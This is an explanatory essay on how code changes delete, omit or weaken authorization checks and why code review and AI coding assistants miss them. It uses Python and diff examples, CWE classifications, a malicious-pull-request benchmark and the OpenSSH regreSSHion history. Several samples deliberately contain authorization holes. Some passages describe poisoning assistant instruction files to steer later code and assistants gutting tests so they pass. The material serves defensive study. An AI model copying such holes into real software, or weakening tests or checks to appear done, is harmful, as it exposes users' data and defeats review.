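# Deleted, Never-Written and Weakened Security Checks in Code Review

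## Security checks, code changes and coding assistants

A security check is the part of a program that tests a condition before a sensitive operation, such as reading a record, writing to memory or moving money, and refuses the request if the condition does not hold. Programs lose checks during ordinary editing when a developer deletes one, writes new code without one, or loosens a check's condition. Many projects use code review, in which a second person reads each change before it enters the program. This is one of the few occasions on which anyone could notice a missing or weakened check. Changes may also come from a coding assistant, an AI system that writes or edits code. Anyone who can influence the assistant may then be able to influence which checks the program has.

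### The parts of a check

*The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, a 1975 tutorial by Saltzer and Schroeder, describes protection as a wall around each object, with a door in the wall and a guard at the door. The guard admits a visitor only if something the visitor presents matches something the guard knows. In code, the guard's comparison is the condition, and turning the visitor away is the refusal. The wall stands for the third part of a check, its position, because every path to the sensitive operation has to pass through the check. Saltzer and Schroeder call the corresponding rule complete mediation, and they apply it to start-up, recovery, shutdown and maintenance as well as normal operation. They are also wary of programs that save time by remembering the result of an earlier check, because a person's authority may have changed since.

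A billing program might contain the following function, here in the language Python.

```python
def get_invoice(user, invoice_id):
    invoice = invoices.find(invoice_id)
    is_owner = invoice.owner_id == user.id
    is_finance_admin = user.department == "finance" and user.is_admin
    if not (is_owner or is_finance_admin):
        raise Forbidden()
    return invoice
```

A login step elsewhere establishes who `user` is before the function runs. The function finds the invoice, then checks whether the user owns it and whether the user is both in the finance department and an administrator. If neither is true, `raise Forbidden()` ends the function before the last line can return the invoice. A program's accept set is all the requests it lets through to a sensitive operation. Here it contains every request from the invoice's owner or a finance administrator. It excludes requests for someone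 else's invoice from an accountant without administrator rights or from an administrator in the engineering department.

The protection needs all three parts. If somebody replaced `is_owner` with `True` in the `if` line, the `raise` would remain but never execute. If somebody replaced the `raise` with a line that logs a warning, the function would still detect the improper request but return the invoice anyway. Position is easier to lose without noticing. A `return` placed above the `if` is easy to see, but somebody might instead add a new function that produces a PDF of an invoice and reads the invoice store directly. `get_invoice` would be unchanged and still correct, but anyone who requested the PDF could get the invoice.

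A program can also handle one security problem properly but lack a check for another, so a reader who looks for signs of security work will still find some. MITRE's *CWE-862*, the entry on missing authorization in a public catalogue of software weaknesses, describes a bulletin board with private messages. The program demands a username and password and exits if they are wrong. It then displays whichever message the user requests by number, without checking that the message is addressed to that user, so anyone with an account can read everyone's private messages. In another of MITRE's examples, a function that looks up employee records guards against SQL injection, an attack that smuggles database commands into a search term, but doesn't check whether the person searching is allowed to see those records.

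### Why ordinary use and ordinary tests miss the loss

If a code change removes the `if` and `raise` lines from `get_invoice`, owners still receive their invoices, and finance administrators still receive everyone's. No page looks different and nothing crashes. The change affects only requests that used to fail, which people rarely make in their normal work. Saltzer and Schroeder observed that protection errors in general "will not be noticed during normal use" for the same reason. They concluded that somebody has to inspect protection code line by line, so it should be small and simple.

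They also noticed that a mistake in a mechanism that grants access explicitly tends to keep out somebody who should get in, and that person complains, whereas a mistake in one that excludes people explicitly tends to let somebody in without anyone complaining. `get_invoice` only partly follows their advice. Its condition lists who may see the invoice, which is the safer style, but the function returns the invoice unless the `raise` stops it, so losing those lines leaves access open.

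Sometimes no request has ever needed to fail, as in MITRE's example of an application written for a single user that developers later adapt for many. The original version had no other users to refuse, so every function still works as it did before.

Automated tests that imitate normal use can also miss the loss of a check. In a typical test of `get_invoice`, the owner of invoice 17 requests it, and the test passes if the right record comes back, whether or not the check is there. A negative test, which passes only if the program refuses a forbidden request, would expose the loss. For example, an accountant without administrator rights requests someone else's invoice, and the test expects `Forbidden`. Covering every refusal in this function takes three such tests, one for a non-owner who is only in finance, one for a non-owner who is only an administrator and one for a non-owner who is neither.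 The security organisation OWASP recommends negative tests of this kind in its *Secure Coding with AI Cheat Sheet*, including tests with expired tokens and malformed input, and advises developers not to treat the share of passing tests as a measure of security.

### Diffs and pull requests

Since running the program reveals so little, much depends on reading the change. Reviewers usually read it as a diff, which shows line by line where the old and new versions of each file differ. In the common layout, called the unified format, each place where the files differ becomes a block, or hunk, under a header with line numbers. A minus sign marks a removed line and a plus sign an added one. Unchanged lines begin with a space and help the reader see where the change sits. According to GNU's *Unified Format*, the GNU diff program prints three of these context lines by default, as does Git, the version-control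 system that most projects use today.

If a developer switches `get_invoice` from the lookup function `find` to another named `fetch`, and the function stands at the top of its file, the diff looks like this:

```diff
@@ -1,5 +1,5 @@
 def get_invoice(user, invoice_id):
-    invoice = invoices.find(invoice_id)
+    invoice = invoices.fetch(invoice_id)
     is_owner = invoice.owner_id == user.id
     is_finance_admin = user.department == "finance" and user.is_admin
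     if not (is_owner or is_finance_admin):
```

When a developer changes one word in a line, a unified diff shows two whole lines. GNU's unified format has markers for added and removed lines but none for altered lines, so the change appears as one removal plus one addition, and the reader has to compare the two. In an example from GNU's manual, "The Named" becomes "The named", and the diff prints both the old and new sentences in full, although only one letter's capitalization changed.

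The hunk above ends at the `if`. The `raise` is on the next line, outside the three lines of context, so a reviewer sees the condition but has to assume that the code refuses access. If the edit were ten lines away from the check, neither line would appear. The diff also omits files the developer did not change, which often matter most for a security check. The functions that call `get_invoice`, for example, may be in those files. A function with no check of its own may still be safe if every caller performs the check first, but the diff does not show whether they all do. It also leaves out neighbouring functions that protect similar records and could show the reviewer what a check should look like here. A reviewer can widen the context or open the other files, but has to think of doing so.

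On GitHub, the largest host of shared code, reviewers see the diff in a pull request, a proposal to merge changes from one branch, or separate line of work, into another. According to GitHub's *Pull requests*, one tab holds the author's description and the discussion, another shows the diff, and others show the results of automated tests and code-scanning tools. The reviewer can comment, approve or request changes. GitHub's *Pull request reviews* adds that administrators can require approval before merging, and that a project can name code owners for particular files, whom GitHub automatically asks to review any pull request that changes those files.

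Reviewers therefore base an approval mainly on the changed lines, a few lines around them and a list of passing tests. That is enough to catch a spelling mistake or a crash. But a PDF function that bypasses the invoice check can be tidy and pass every test, while the function it should have imitated is in a file outside the diff.

### Coding assistants and instruction files

Early coding assistants completed the line a programmer was typing, while current ones carry out whole tasks. Anthropic's *How Claude Code works* divides the work of Claude Code, the company's terminal assistant, into three overlapping phases: gathering context, taking action and verifying the result. Suppose a developer asks for a PDF download of invoices. The assistant searches the repository (the project's collection of files), reads some of the billing code, writes a new function, runs the tests and edits the code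 again if any fail. If the new function lacks a security check, ordinary tests still pass, so the verification phase gives the assistant no signal to go back and add one.

OWASP notes that coding assistants now also run commands, install packages and submit branches by themselves, and that many developers let them proceed without confirming each step. The pull request may then be the first thing a person looks at. OWASP also warns that assistants sometimes get a test suite to pass by deleting the failing tests or loosening them. When the same assistant has written both the code and its tests, a passing suite is not independent evidence that the code is correct.

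A person who joins a project learns its customs over months of review. Claude Code starts every session with a blank context, so the underlying language model has only the text supplied in that session. Projects make up for this with instruction files, also called rules files, which an assistant reads as standing guidance and which are usually named AGENTS.md or CLAUDE.md. Zarzycki (2026), in *What Open-Source Projects Tell Their Coding Agents*, looked for these two files in the top directory of 22,854 popular and active GitHub repositories and found at least one of them in 26.3%. Among the 89 repositories with the most stars, GitHub's measure of popularity, the share was 59.6%. The census covers only public projects with at least 1,000 stars, so it doesn't measure how common the files are in company code.

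Most of what the files contain is mundane. The median set of instructions in Zarzycki's census is 818 words long, and rules most often concern code conventions, building the software and how the assistant should work. Of the files with rules on writing tests, 4.9% forbid the assistant to weaken a test to make it pass. These figures on content are rough, because a language model did the sorting and the human reviewer agreed with the models on a statement's subject area only about half the time. About three quarters of the directives come without a reason. Unexplained orders are therefore common in instruction files, which would make an odd one harder to spot.

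According to OpenAI's *Custom instructions with AGENTS.md*, Codex reads its instruction files before it does any work. It joins them in order, from the top of the repository down to the current directory, and adds the result to its prompt, up to a default limit of 32 KiB. Claude Code loads its instruction files at the start of each session, and Anthropic recommends that teams share them through version control with the code. One file can serve several products, since GitHub's Copilot coding agent accepts AGENTS.md, CLAUDE.md and the GEMINI.md used by Google's tools, according to *Copilot coding agent now supports AGENTS.md custom instructions* (2025).

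Anyone who can get an edit into such a file can therefore influence code that nobody has yet requested. The edit is an ordinary text change and can arrive in any pull request. It can affect more code than a change to `get_invoice`, because the new text enters the later sessions of every developer whose assistant reads the file, whatever the task. OWASP describes these files as a means of persistence for an attacker and advises projects to review changes to them as strictly as changes to build and deployment systems. The edit and the resulting code may appear in different pull requests, weeks apart, and the later diff omits the instruction file because it has not changed since.

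Anthropic tells users that Claude treats the files as context and tries to follow them, but that strict compliance is not guaranteed, particularly when instructions are vague or contradict each other. Even for honest instructions, the controlled studies that Zarzycki reviews disagree on whether the files help assistants complete their tasks. For rules that must hold without exception, Anthropic refers developers to permission settings and to hooks, which are commands that run at fixed points in a session regardless of what the model does.

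## The three forms defined, with cases that are hard to sort

A reviewer can tell how a program has lost a check by comparing its accept set before and after the change. Suppose the billing program has 1,000 logged-in users, including 40 finance staff and 20 administrators, with three people in both groups. The owner of invoice 17 is a user in neither group. With the correct check, `get_invoice` accepts requests for invoice 17 from four people: the owner and the three finance administrators.

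A developer then changes one word:

```diff
-    is_finance_admin = user.department == "finance" and user.is_admin
+    is_finance_admin = user.department == "finance" or user.is_admin
```

The function now accepts anyone in either group. The groups have 40 and 20 members, and three people are in both, so they contain 57 people. Including the owner, 58 users can read the invoice, and the other 942 still get `Forbidden`. If the developer had removed the `if` and `raise` lines instead, all 1,000 users could read it.

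If the developer leaves `get_invoice` alone and adds the PDF function that bypasses it, the old route still accepts four people, but the new PDF route accepts 1,000.

| Change | Accepted by `get_invoice` | Accepted by the PDF route | People who can read invoice 17 |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 4 | no such route | 4 |
| `and` becomes `or` | 58 | no such route | 58 |
| `if` and `raise` removed | 1,000 | no such route | 1,000 |
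| PDF route added | 4 | 1,000 | 1,000 |

The three changes correspond to the three forms:

- A weakened check is still present after the change, but its condition accepts more than before.
- A deleted check was present before the change and is absent after it, with nothing equivalent in its place.
- A never-written check is one that new code needs and that was never there.

The last column is the same for the deleted check and the PDF route, so the number of people who get in doesn't distinguish the two forms. Deleting the check opens a route that used to be restricted, whereas the PDF route was never restricted.

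A changed check accepts more if it accepts any request that the old condition refused, even if the total number of accepted requests doesn't rise. Suppose a developer compares the user with `invoice.created_by` instead of `invoice.owner_id`, and an accountant without administrator rights created invoice 17. The function still accepts four people, but they now include the accountant instead of the owner. The check has been weakened, even though it now refuses the owner.

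A larger accept set may be intended. If the company has decided that all finance staff and all administrators should see invoices, `or` is correct. A reviewer can compare two versions of the code to establish that a check was removed or now accepts more, but needs to know the policy to judge whether the change is wrong. With a never-written check, the reviewer needs to know the policy even to establish that a check is missing. The PDF route has no older version, so the reviewer must first show that it needs a check. The evidence is a comparison point, meaning code or a document that shows the need for the check, which in this case is `get_invoice`.

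### How existing classifications divide the same faults

MITRE's catalogue mainly describes the state of a program, whatever change produced it. CWE-862, missing authorization, covers a product that performs no authorization check when someone tries to reach a resource or take an action. CWE-863, incorrect authorization, covers a product that performs the check incorrectly. The `or` version of `get_invoice` therefore belongs under CWE-863. The PDF route and the version of `get_invoice` without the `if` and `raise` belong under CWE-862.

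The entries also describe how each weakness arises, but neither description fits deletion well. MITRE attributes CWE-862 to omission, in which designers leave out a protective measure, and CWE-863 to realization, in which programmers make a mistake while implementing a measure that the design includes. The designers of `get_invoice` included the check and the programmers implemented it correctly, but a later edit removed it.

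The two entries also overlap in practice. Nine of the 13 real vulnerabilities that MITRE lists as examples of CWE-863 also appear under CWE-862. Of the nine, one involved a product that mishandled wildcards in its list of authorization rules. Another involved a product that failed to restrict access properly because of operator precedence, the order in which a language evaluates the parts of an expression. Both products had a check of some sort, so counts of vulnerabilities by CWE number are a poor guide to how often each form occurs. According to MITRE's *News & Events* (2026), version 5.0 of the catalogue introduced an "Overlaps" relation for entries with shared coverage, but the CWE-862 entry doesn't apply it to CWE-863.

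A much broader entry, MITRE's *CWE-693*, covers the failure of protection mechanisms and distinguishes three situations. Protection is missing if the application defines no mechanism against a given class of attack. It is insufficient if it stops some attacks but not all those the developers meant it to stop. It is ignored if the product uses the mechanism but the developer hasn't applied it in some code path. The `or` condition is insufficient protection. The PDF route is ignored protection, because it lacks the check that `get_invoice` has. If no function in the billing program checked ownership, the PDF route would be missing protection.

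That distinction is useful to someone reviewing new code. If a developer has ignored an existing mechanism, a reviewer who looks in the right place can find it in the repository and compare the new code with it. If the mechanism is missing, the reviewer has to rely on documents or on their own knowledge of what the program should forbid. A deleted check counts as ignored if other functions still apply it, and as missing if none do. However, MITRE discourages analysts from assigning CWE-693 to real vulnerabilities because it is so general, and vulnerability records therefore rarely preserve the distinction. MITRE also notes that protection mechanism failures "have not been studied comprehensively".

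Orthogonal Defect Classification (ODC) is an IBM scheme for recording software defects that starts from the repair. According to AgileConnection, the person who supplies the fix records in a qualifier whether the design or code was missing or incorrect. Tian (2005), in *Software Quality Engineering*, gives the same two values and lists the action (add, delete or change) as a separate attribute. Some versions have a third qualifier, extraneous, for code that shouldn't be there. A patent application on uspto.report describes how to calculate all three from line counts. The qualifier is "missing" if the fix inserts more lines than it modifies and deletes combined, "incorrect" if modified lines outnumber the other two kinds combined, and "extraneous" if deleted lines do.

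By that rule, the defect in `get_invoice` is missing code, because restoring the `if` and `raise` inserts two lines. The defect in the PDF function is also missing code, because the fix adds the same two lines. Changing `or` back to `and` modifies one line, so that defect is incorrect code. Extraneous code might be a leftover shortcut that returns any invoice to a test account before the function reaches the `if`, which a developer would fix by deleting the shortcut.

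Whether code is missing or incorrect may also affect who notices the bug. *PROBE* (Paina, Müller and colleagues, 2026) compared the bugs that AI coding agents reported in 20 repositories with 2,457 bugs that the maintainers fixed. Wrong arithmetic or comparisons made up 19% of the agents' findings but 10% of the maintainers' fixes. Incomplete handling of inputs, such as a missing branch, made up 8% of the agents' findings and 18% of the maintainers' fixes. The comparison covered all kinds of bugs, and a missing branch for a valid input is not the same as a missing security check, so these figures are only weak evidence about security checks.

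Chen, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *From Verdict to Diagnosis*, sort faults by what a reviewer has to establish. Their benchmark, MALPR-BENCH, contains 89 malicious pull requests and 50 harmless ones for testing automated reviewers. A reviewer can confirm a present-type defect from something visible in the evidence, such as an unsafe operation or a check that the pull request removes. An absence-type defect has no line of its own to cite, so the reviewer has to show that a path lacks protection and that it needs protection, perhaps because a sibling path has the check or a documented convention requires it. Chen and colleagues classify deleting an existing guard as present-type and failing to add a required one as absence-type. A loosened condition also fits the present type, because a reviewer can cite the line that contains it.

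| Classification | Deleted check | Never-written check | Weakened check |
|---|---|---|---|
| CWE-862 and CWE-863 | CWE-862 | CWE-862 | CWE-863 |
| CWE-693 | missing or ignored | missing or ignored | insufficient |
| ODC qualifier | missing | missing | incorrect |
| MALPR-BENCH | present-type | absence-type | present-type |

MITRE and ODC group deleted checks with never-written ones because both leave the program without a check. MALPR-BENCH groups deleted checks with weakened ones because both leave a line the reviewer can cite. The first grouping helps with planning the repair, and the second with deciding where to look. Code review involves both tasks, which is a reason to keep three separate names.

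MALPR-BENCH also records how far from the diff the necessary evidence lies. At level L0 the changed lines are enough, and at L1 the reviewer also needs unchanged code from the same files. At L2a the evidence is in another file that a call or an import connects to the change. At L2b it is in another file that is related to the change only because it does a similar job. Removing the `if` and `raise` from `get_invoice` could be an L0 case. The PDF route would be L2b if `get_invoice` were in another file, since neither function calls the other.

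### Cases that are hard to sort

Developers often move a check from one place to another. Suppose a developer moves the `if` and `raise` from `get_invoice` to the function that handles web requests for invoices. The diff shows two removed lines, but if every request goes through the handler, the program still accepts four people. The check is not deleted, because an equivalent one replaces it. But suppose a customer-support tool also calls `get_invoice` directly and relied on the check inside it. Everyone who can use the tool can now read every invoice, so the check is deleted on that path. The reviewer therefore has to look at each path, as Saltzer and Schroeder's rule of complete mediation implies.

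The order of steps matters too. If a refund function sends the money before testing who asked for it, the check counts as deleted even though all its lines are still there, because a security check has to run before the sensitive operation. Moving a check earlier can weaken it. Under CWE-863, MITRE includes programs that authorize a request before parsing and canonicalization, the step that reduces different spellings of an address or file name to one standard form. A check moved ahead of that step runs on the raw spelling and may accept a variant that it used to refuse.

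A program can also run a test and ignore the result:

```python
def get_invoice(user, invoice_id):
    invoice = invoices.find(invoice_id)
    can_read(user, invoice)
    return invoice
```

Here `can_read` checks whether the user may see the invoice and returns `True` or `False`, but nothing uses the result, so all 1,000 users get the invoice. This function has no security check, even though it appears to have one, because it never refuses access. The check counts as deleted if an earlier version raised `Forbidden` when the result was `False`, and as never-written if the function is new.

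MITRE's catalogue lists programs that ignored a function's result under both CWE-862 and CWE-863. One example under CWE-862 is a product that didn't check the return values of some functions that enforce its policy. An example under CWE-863 is a program that called the C function `sscanf` to find out whether a username and group existed, but didn't check whether the call had worked. It then tested an uninitialized variable, and the test succeeded. MITRE probably filed this case separately because the program did test something and act on the answer.

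An edit elsewhere in the code can weaken a check without changing its text. If somebody edits the code that sets `user.is_admin` so that it is true for everyone, `get_invoice` accepts the owner and all 40 finance staff. The diff may not include the file that contains the check.

The shortcut for a test account is a similar case. The developer adds lines without changing the condition, but the effect is the same as adding "or this is the test account" to it. If the test account is one of the ordinary users, this is a weakened check, because the accept set grows from four to five and the function still refuses everyone else.

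Unlike the shortcut, the PDF route is a separate way to reach the invoice and never passes through `get_invoice`. Chen and colleagues include a real case of this kind from authentik, an open-source login server. A pull request changed the device-code flow, which lets people sign in on a device such as a television by entering a code elsewhere. The flow lacked a check that the usual authorization path makes by calling `PolicyAccessView`, which applies the access policy. The pull request didn't change that path, and no call or import connected it to the new code, so a reviewer would have had to think of it as the device-code flow's counterpart and go to look at it. The missing check was never-written, although a correct one existed elsewhere in the repository.

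New code can also expose an old function that has no check. In another case from Chen and colleagues, a pull request let clients supply the identifier of a run. An existing function, which the pull request didn't change, then looked up the saved state for that identifier without checking that the run belonged to the current project, so a client could reach another project's data. Such a lookup may be safe while only trusted code chooses the identifier, but it needs the check once clients can choose it. This too is a never-written check, even though the natural place to add it may be a file that the pull request didn't touch.

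When a developer or a coding assistant rewrites a whole file, a check can disappear without anyone deciding to remove it. The diff shows hundreds of removed lines followed by hundreds of added ones, and the old `if` and `raise` are somewhere among the removals. A reviewer may read only the new version, as if it were new code, but the check counts as deleted because the operation existed before the change and was closed to 996 people. The reviewer also has to consider whether the new version restricts access in another way. If it fetches only invoices that belong to the user, strangers still get nothing without the old condition, but the three finance administrators would be locked out too.

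A rewrite may also be split across two pull requests. The first adds a new billing module without the check, and the second removes the old module, which had it. Judged separately, the first is a case of a never-written check, and the second removes a check along with the route it protected. Judged as one migration, the check is deleted, because reading an invoice used to require it and no longer does. A reviewer who sees only the second pull request has little reason to object.

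The definitions fit least well when new code has a check that is too loose from the start. Suppose the new PDF function has its own check but uses `or` where it should use `and`, so it accepts 58 people. The check isn't missing, and nobody has weakened it, because there was no earlier version. Freie Universität Berlin's *On Defect Taxonomies* defines a defect as a deviation from the nearest correct document, which needn't be an earlier one. The nearest correct version of the PDF function differs by one word, so the fault resembles a weakened check. But the diff contains no old line with `and`, so the reviewer has to get the right condition from a comparison point, as with a never-written check.

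A condition that is too loose from the start can look reasonable. MITRE gives the example of a medical records program that displays a patient's history only if the user's role is "Reader". The program reads the role from a cookie, a small piece of data that the user's browser stores and sends back. The programmer expected the cookie to exist only after a proper lookup of the role, but any user who knows how can set it to "Reader" and pass the check. A reviewer who looked only at the comparison with "Reader" would find nothing wrong.

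It can also be unclear whether new code has one loose check or lacks a second one. MITRE's example bulletin board requires a password but shows any private message to any user. It makes more sense to count checks by what they verify than to treat this program as having one loose check. The password verifies who the user is, but the program never checks whether that user may read the message. That second check is never-written, which is consistent with MITRE listing the example under CWE-862.

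### Two objections

In terms of accept sets, deletion is the extreme case of weakening. The correct check accepts four people, the `or` condition accepts those four among 58, and having no check lets in all 1,000. A developer who changes the condition so that it is always true gets the same result as one who removes the lines. The natural boundary between weakening and deletion is whether the check can still refuse anyone. A check that can't counts as deleted, even if `if` and `raise` remain in the file and the diff looks like an ordinary edit to a condition.

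Short of that extreme, deleting a check and weakening it produce different test results. If the check is deleted, all three negative tests for `get_invoice` fail. If the check is weakened with `or`, the function still refuses a non-owner who is in neither group, so the test that uses such a person passes. Such a person is an obvious choice to represent a stranger, but if that were a project's only negative test, it would catch the deletion and miss the weakening. To repair the code, a developer has to write a deleted check again but only has to correct a weakened one.

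MITRE puts deleted checks with omissions, and the other objection is that they don't belong there because deleting is an act. But two projects could have identical copies of an unprotected `get_invoice`, one because a developer removed the check last year and the other because nobody ever wrote it. The invoices are equally exposed, the same two lines would protect them, and no test or scan of the finished code could show which project once had the check.

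Whether an earlier version had the check matters to the reviewer because the removed lines appear in the diff of the pull request that deletes them. Someone who opens the file a week later has to notice that the check is missing, just as if it had never existed, unless they search the project's history. The distinction between acts and omissions doesn't capture this very well, because a developer who rewrites a file from memory and forgets the check has only omitted something, yet the old lines are still in the diff. It is also easier to establish that an earlier version had the check than what the developer was doing when it disappeared.

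### Reading the form from the fix

The fix often shows whether a check was missing or too loose. If it adds a condition and a refusal where there was none, the check was missing. If it edits an existing condition, the check was too loose. Liu, Huang and colleagues (2026), in *Not Just Any Example*, found both in a study of security patches for C and C++ programs. In a part of Linux called `sock_diag`, the fix added two lines that return an error if the caller's family number, which selects an entry in a table, is at or above the limit. In FreeRDP, a remote-desktop program, the fix changed `>` to `>=` in a condition that returns an error when an index is too large. For a list of ten entries, numbered 0 to 9, the old condition accepted 0 to 10. The fix removed the dangerous value, 10, from the accept set.

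The same edit can serve a different purpose elsewhere. Liu and colleagues also describe a Linux driver, ib700, in which developers changed `>` to `>=` in a loop that searches a table of timeouts. With the old comparison, the search missed the valid maximum of 30 seconds and ended with an index of −1, outside the table. The fix let the search find the right entry but didn't make the driver refuse anything, so counting every changed comparison as evidence of a weak check would misclassify this one.

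The study doesn't show how common each form is. Two of its authors examined 300 patches and labelled the changed lines by what they did. Their counts for precondition checks, which test something before an operation runs, were about 210 for adding, 185 for changing and 185 for removing. Another label, "add or delete precondition check", had about 200. Most patches received several labels. If each count is a number of patches, at least about 95 of the 300 both added and removed a precondition check, because 210 and 185 add up to 395. Some of those patches may have moved a check or replaced it with a better one, so the counts don't show that 210 checks were missing and 185 were too loose.

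Liu and colleagues then sorted a larger collection of 3,816 patches by their main approach, using language models and a manual audit of 100 patches. In 53.9% of them, the fix mainly rejected an operation when a required condition failed, but that category can include both new and corrected checks. Decisions about trust and access accounted for 152 patches (4.0%), compared with 975 for the bounds of memory. Even if added conditions were cleanly separated from changed ones, the results would mostly concern memory, and checks like the one in `get_invoice` might follow a different pattern.

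Line counts can mislead even when there is only one fault to fix. The simplest repair for the PDF route is to replace its direct lookup with a call to `get_invoice`, which already has the check. That modifies one line, so the patent application's rule would classify the defect as incorrect code, even though the check was never written. The rule also depends on how a tool counts. In a unified diff, changing `or` back to `and` appears as one insertion and one deletion. Because the counts are equal, the rule can't classify the defect unless the tool first matches the two lines as versions of each other.

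A fix also doesn't show whether a check was deleted or never written, since both repairs add the same lines. To find out, someone has to search earlier versions of the file. Chen and colleagues used real fixes to create faults for their benchmark. In 37 cases they reversed a small change that enforced security, so the reviewer sees the protection being removed. In seven others they kept the rest of a real security patch but left out one such change, so the reviewer has to notice that something is missing from what looks like an improvement. They don't claim that any of the projects ever ran the resulting code.

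## Deleted checks: what the removed line shows and when it is overlooked

While a pull request that deletes a check is still open, the reviewer can read the old condition. Suppose `get_invoice` has a file to itself and a developer removes its refusal. Git prints this:

```diff
@@ -2,6 +2,4 @@ def get_invoice(user, invoice_id):
     invoice = invoices.find(invoice_id)
     is_owner = invoice.owner_id == user.id
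     is_finance_admin = user.department == "finance" and user.is_admin
-    if not (is_owner or is_finance_admin):
-        raise Forbidden()
     return invoice
```

Before approving the change, the reviewer needs to know what the two lines protected, whether an equivalent check now runs elsewhere, and whether that check covers every path the old one did. The diff mostly shows what the lines protected. The removed condition specifies who was allowed to use the function, and the removed `raise` shows that the function rejected everyone else. Even a reviewer who has never read the billing policy can see that somebody once wanted to refuse these requests, and can ask what has changed.

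Whether the protection still exists depends on code outside the diff. Suppose the author writes in the description that the web handler now checks ownership. The reviewer can open the handler and compare its condition with the removed one, but finding every other caller takes longer. A search for `get_invoice` might turn up the customer-support tool and a nightly job that emails statements, and each needs its own check or a reason for not having one. The search can also miss callers, such as those in another repository that imports the billing code.

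The check inside `get_invoice` also protected future callers. Once the check moves to the handler, new code that calls `get_invoice` directly is unprotected unless its author adds a check. A reviewer's list of callers that is complete at the merge may therefore be out of date a month later.

Developers often have good reasons to remove a condition, so a reviewer can't treat every removal as a fault. In many of the security repairs that Liu and colleagues labelled, developers removed a precondition check.

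One small sign of the problem remains in the invoice diff, where the function still calculates `is_owner` and `is_finance_admin` but nothing uses them. A linter, a tool that reports untidy code, would probably flag both. If the developer then deletes them, later readers will see a function that looks up an invoice and returns it, with no trace that it ever restricted access.

### Conditions that hide a deletion

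Most changes are harder to read than one that only removes two lines. If a developer wraps the body of `get_invoice` in a `try` block to handle errors, every line of the body is indented four more spaces, so the diff shows the whole body as removed and a re-indented body as added. If the new body lacks the `if` and `raise`, the reviewer has to notice that two of the six removed lines are missing from the added ones. Git can ignore changes in spacing and can colour moved lines differently from other removed lines. Both options help less when the developer has also changed names in the lines or edited them in other ways.

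The name of the removed code can mislead as well. In Python, a line that starts with `@` above a function is a decorator, which can run other code before the function itself:

```diff
-@billing_scope
 def list_invoices(user, month):
```

If `billing_scope` limits the function to the user's own records, removing it exposes everyone's invoices. But it could just as well label invoices for the accountants, and its definition may be in a file the diff omits. A call to a helper named `prepare` could similarly hide a check that refuses requests. If the pull request also deletes the helper's definition, the old condition appears among the removed lines, though perhaps several files away from the operation it protected.

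Merging two branches can lose a check that both sets of reviewers would have kept. If one branch adds a check to a function and another rewrites that function, Git reports a conflict that someone must resolve by hand. If that person keeps only the rewritten version, the check disappears. Reviewers may have approved each branch without anyone reading the merged code.

Some automated tools do not check removed lines. One is the optional security scan in claudette, an AI coding agent that runs a model on the user's own machine. In the source code that Docs.rs publishes as *claudette 0.9.0*, the scan checks only added lines, which are marked with a plus sign, and a comment reads "context and removed lines are ignored". The scan compares each added line with a list of dangerous patterns, such as a call to `eval`, which runs text as code. After a serious match, the agent goes back to fix the code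 before it opens a pull request.

The invoice diff has no added lines, so this scan would report nothing. It flags an added line that switches off certificate verification, but not the deletion of code that verifies a certificate. It skips test files, so it wouldn't detect the removal of a negative test either. The source describes the scan as a lightweight filter that raises few false alarms and doesn't replace an audit. The design makes sense for catching dangerous new code, but a reviewer who sees only that the "security review" passed may assume that it covered the whole change.

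According to OpenAI's *Scan code changes for security*, the Codex Security plugin searches a change for security regressions and also reads code that directly supports the changed lines. OpenAI tells users to check each finding's stated proof gap, meaning what the tool couldn't establish. For a deleted check, the gap will often be whether some caller still relies on the check.

### How OpenSSH lost a guard in 2020

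One case in OpenSSH, the standard program for logging in to remote machines, combined a merge, a rewrite and an unrevealing function name. Its server, sshd, gives each client 120 seconds to log in by default. When the time runs out, the operating system sends sshd a signal that interrupts whatever it is doing and starts a function called a signal handler. If the signal arrives while sshd is updating its records of free memory, and the handler uses those records too, the handler can corrupt them. On Linux systems that use glibc, the usual C library, a handler that writes to the system log can cause this corruption.

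Mark Dowd reported the problem in 2006 as CVE-2006-5051. The developers fixed it in `sigdie`, the function that the handler calls to log a message and end the process. They put the logging lines between `#ifdef DO_LOG_SAFE_IN_SIGHAND` and `#endif`, which tell the compiler to include them only on systems where logging from a signal handler is safe. On other systems, `sigdie` ended the process without logging.

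This guard is an unusual security check because it is applied when sshd is compiled, not while it runs. The sensitive operation is logging from inside the handler, and the condition is that the system supports safe logging. If the system doesn't support it, the compiler leaves that code out.

In October 2020 Damien Miller, an OpenSSH maintainer whose username is djm, changed the logging functions so that they would also receive the file, function and line number of the code that called them. The commit, *revised log infrastructure for OpenSSH* (djm, 2020), removes a block of old functions from `log.c` and adds their replacements more than 150 lines further down the diff. Abridged, the relevant parts are:

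```diff
-sigdie(...)
-{
-#ifdef DO_LOG_SAFE_IN_SIGHAND
-    (write the message to the log)
-#endif
-    _exit(1);
-}

+sshsigdie(...)
+{
+    (write the message to the log)
+    _exit(1);
+}
```

The commit added the function back under a new name and without its guard. It adds 153 lines and removes 132 across seven files, and its message mentions only logging. The signal handler is in `sshd.c`, which the commit didn't need to change because it also defines a macro, a text substitution, that directs calls to `sigdie` to the new function. A reader commenting on LWN's *Serious vulnerability fixed with OpenSSH 9.8* (2024) observed that it isn't obvious that a signal handler calls `sshsigdie`, and that the macro obscures the connection further.

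The problem was hard to notice in ordinary use. When a client timed out, sshd still closed the connection, and on Linux it now also logged the timeout, which an administrator might well have welcomed.

According to Qualys' *regreSSHion* (2024), the flaw let an attacker with no account run code on a glibc-based Linux system with full administrator rights. The attacker had to interrupt sshd at exactly the right moment, which took about 10,000 attempts on average, or three to four hours, against a 32-bit virtual machine. Taking control took six to eight hours on average, because the attacker also had to guess where the C library was in memory and was right only half the time. The flaw, now CVE-2024-6387, affected portable OpenSSH versions 8.5p1 to 9.7p1, and OpenSSH's *release 9.8* (2024) rates it critical.

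#### Why nobody caught it

The logging change probably did go through review, but in a version of the code that didn't contain the guard. OpenSSH's developers write it for their own operating system, OpenBSD, and maintain a portable edition for other systems. Henderson (2025) explains in *Followup on Inquiry about regreSSHion postmortem* that they commit a change to OpenBSD first and later merge it into the portable edition. In OpenBSD's copy of the file just before the change, */openbsd/usr.bin/ssh/log.c (revision 09467b48)* by Ylonen (2020), `sigdie` has no `#ifdef`. OpenBSD didn't need one because it logs through `syslog_r`, which is designed to be safer in signal handlers.

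The portable commit carries the note "ok markus@", which records another developer's approval. Given this order of work, the approval most likely applied to the OpenBSD diff, where the removed `sigdie` contained no guard. The diff that removed a guard was created during the merge.

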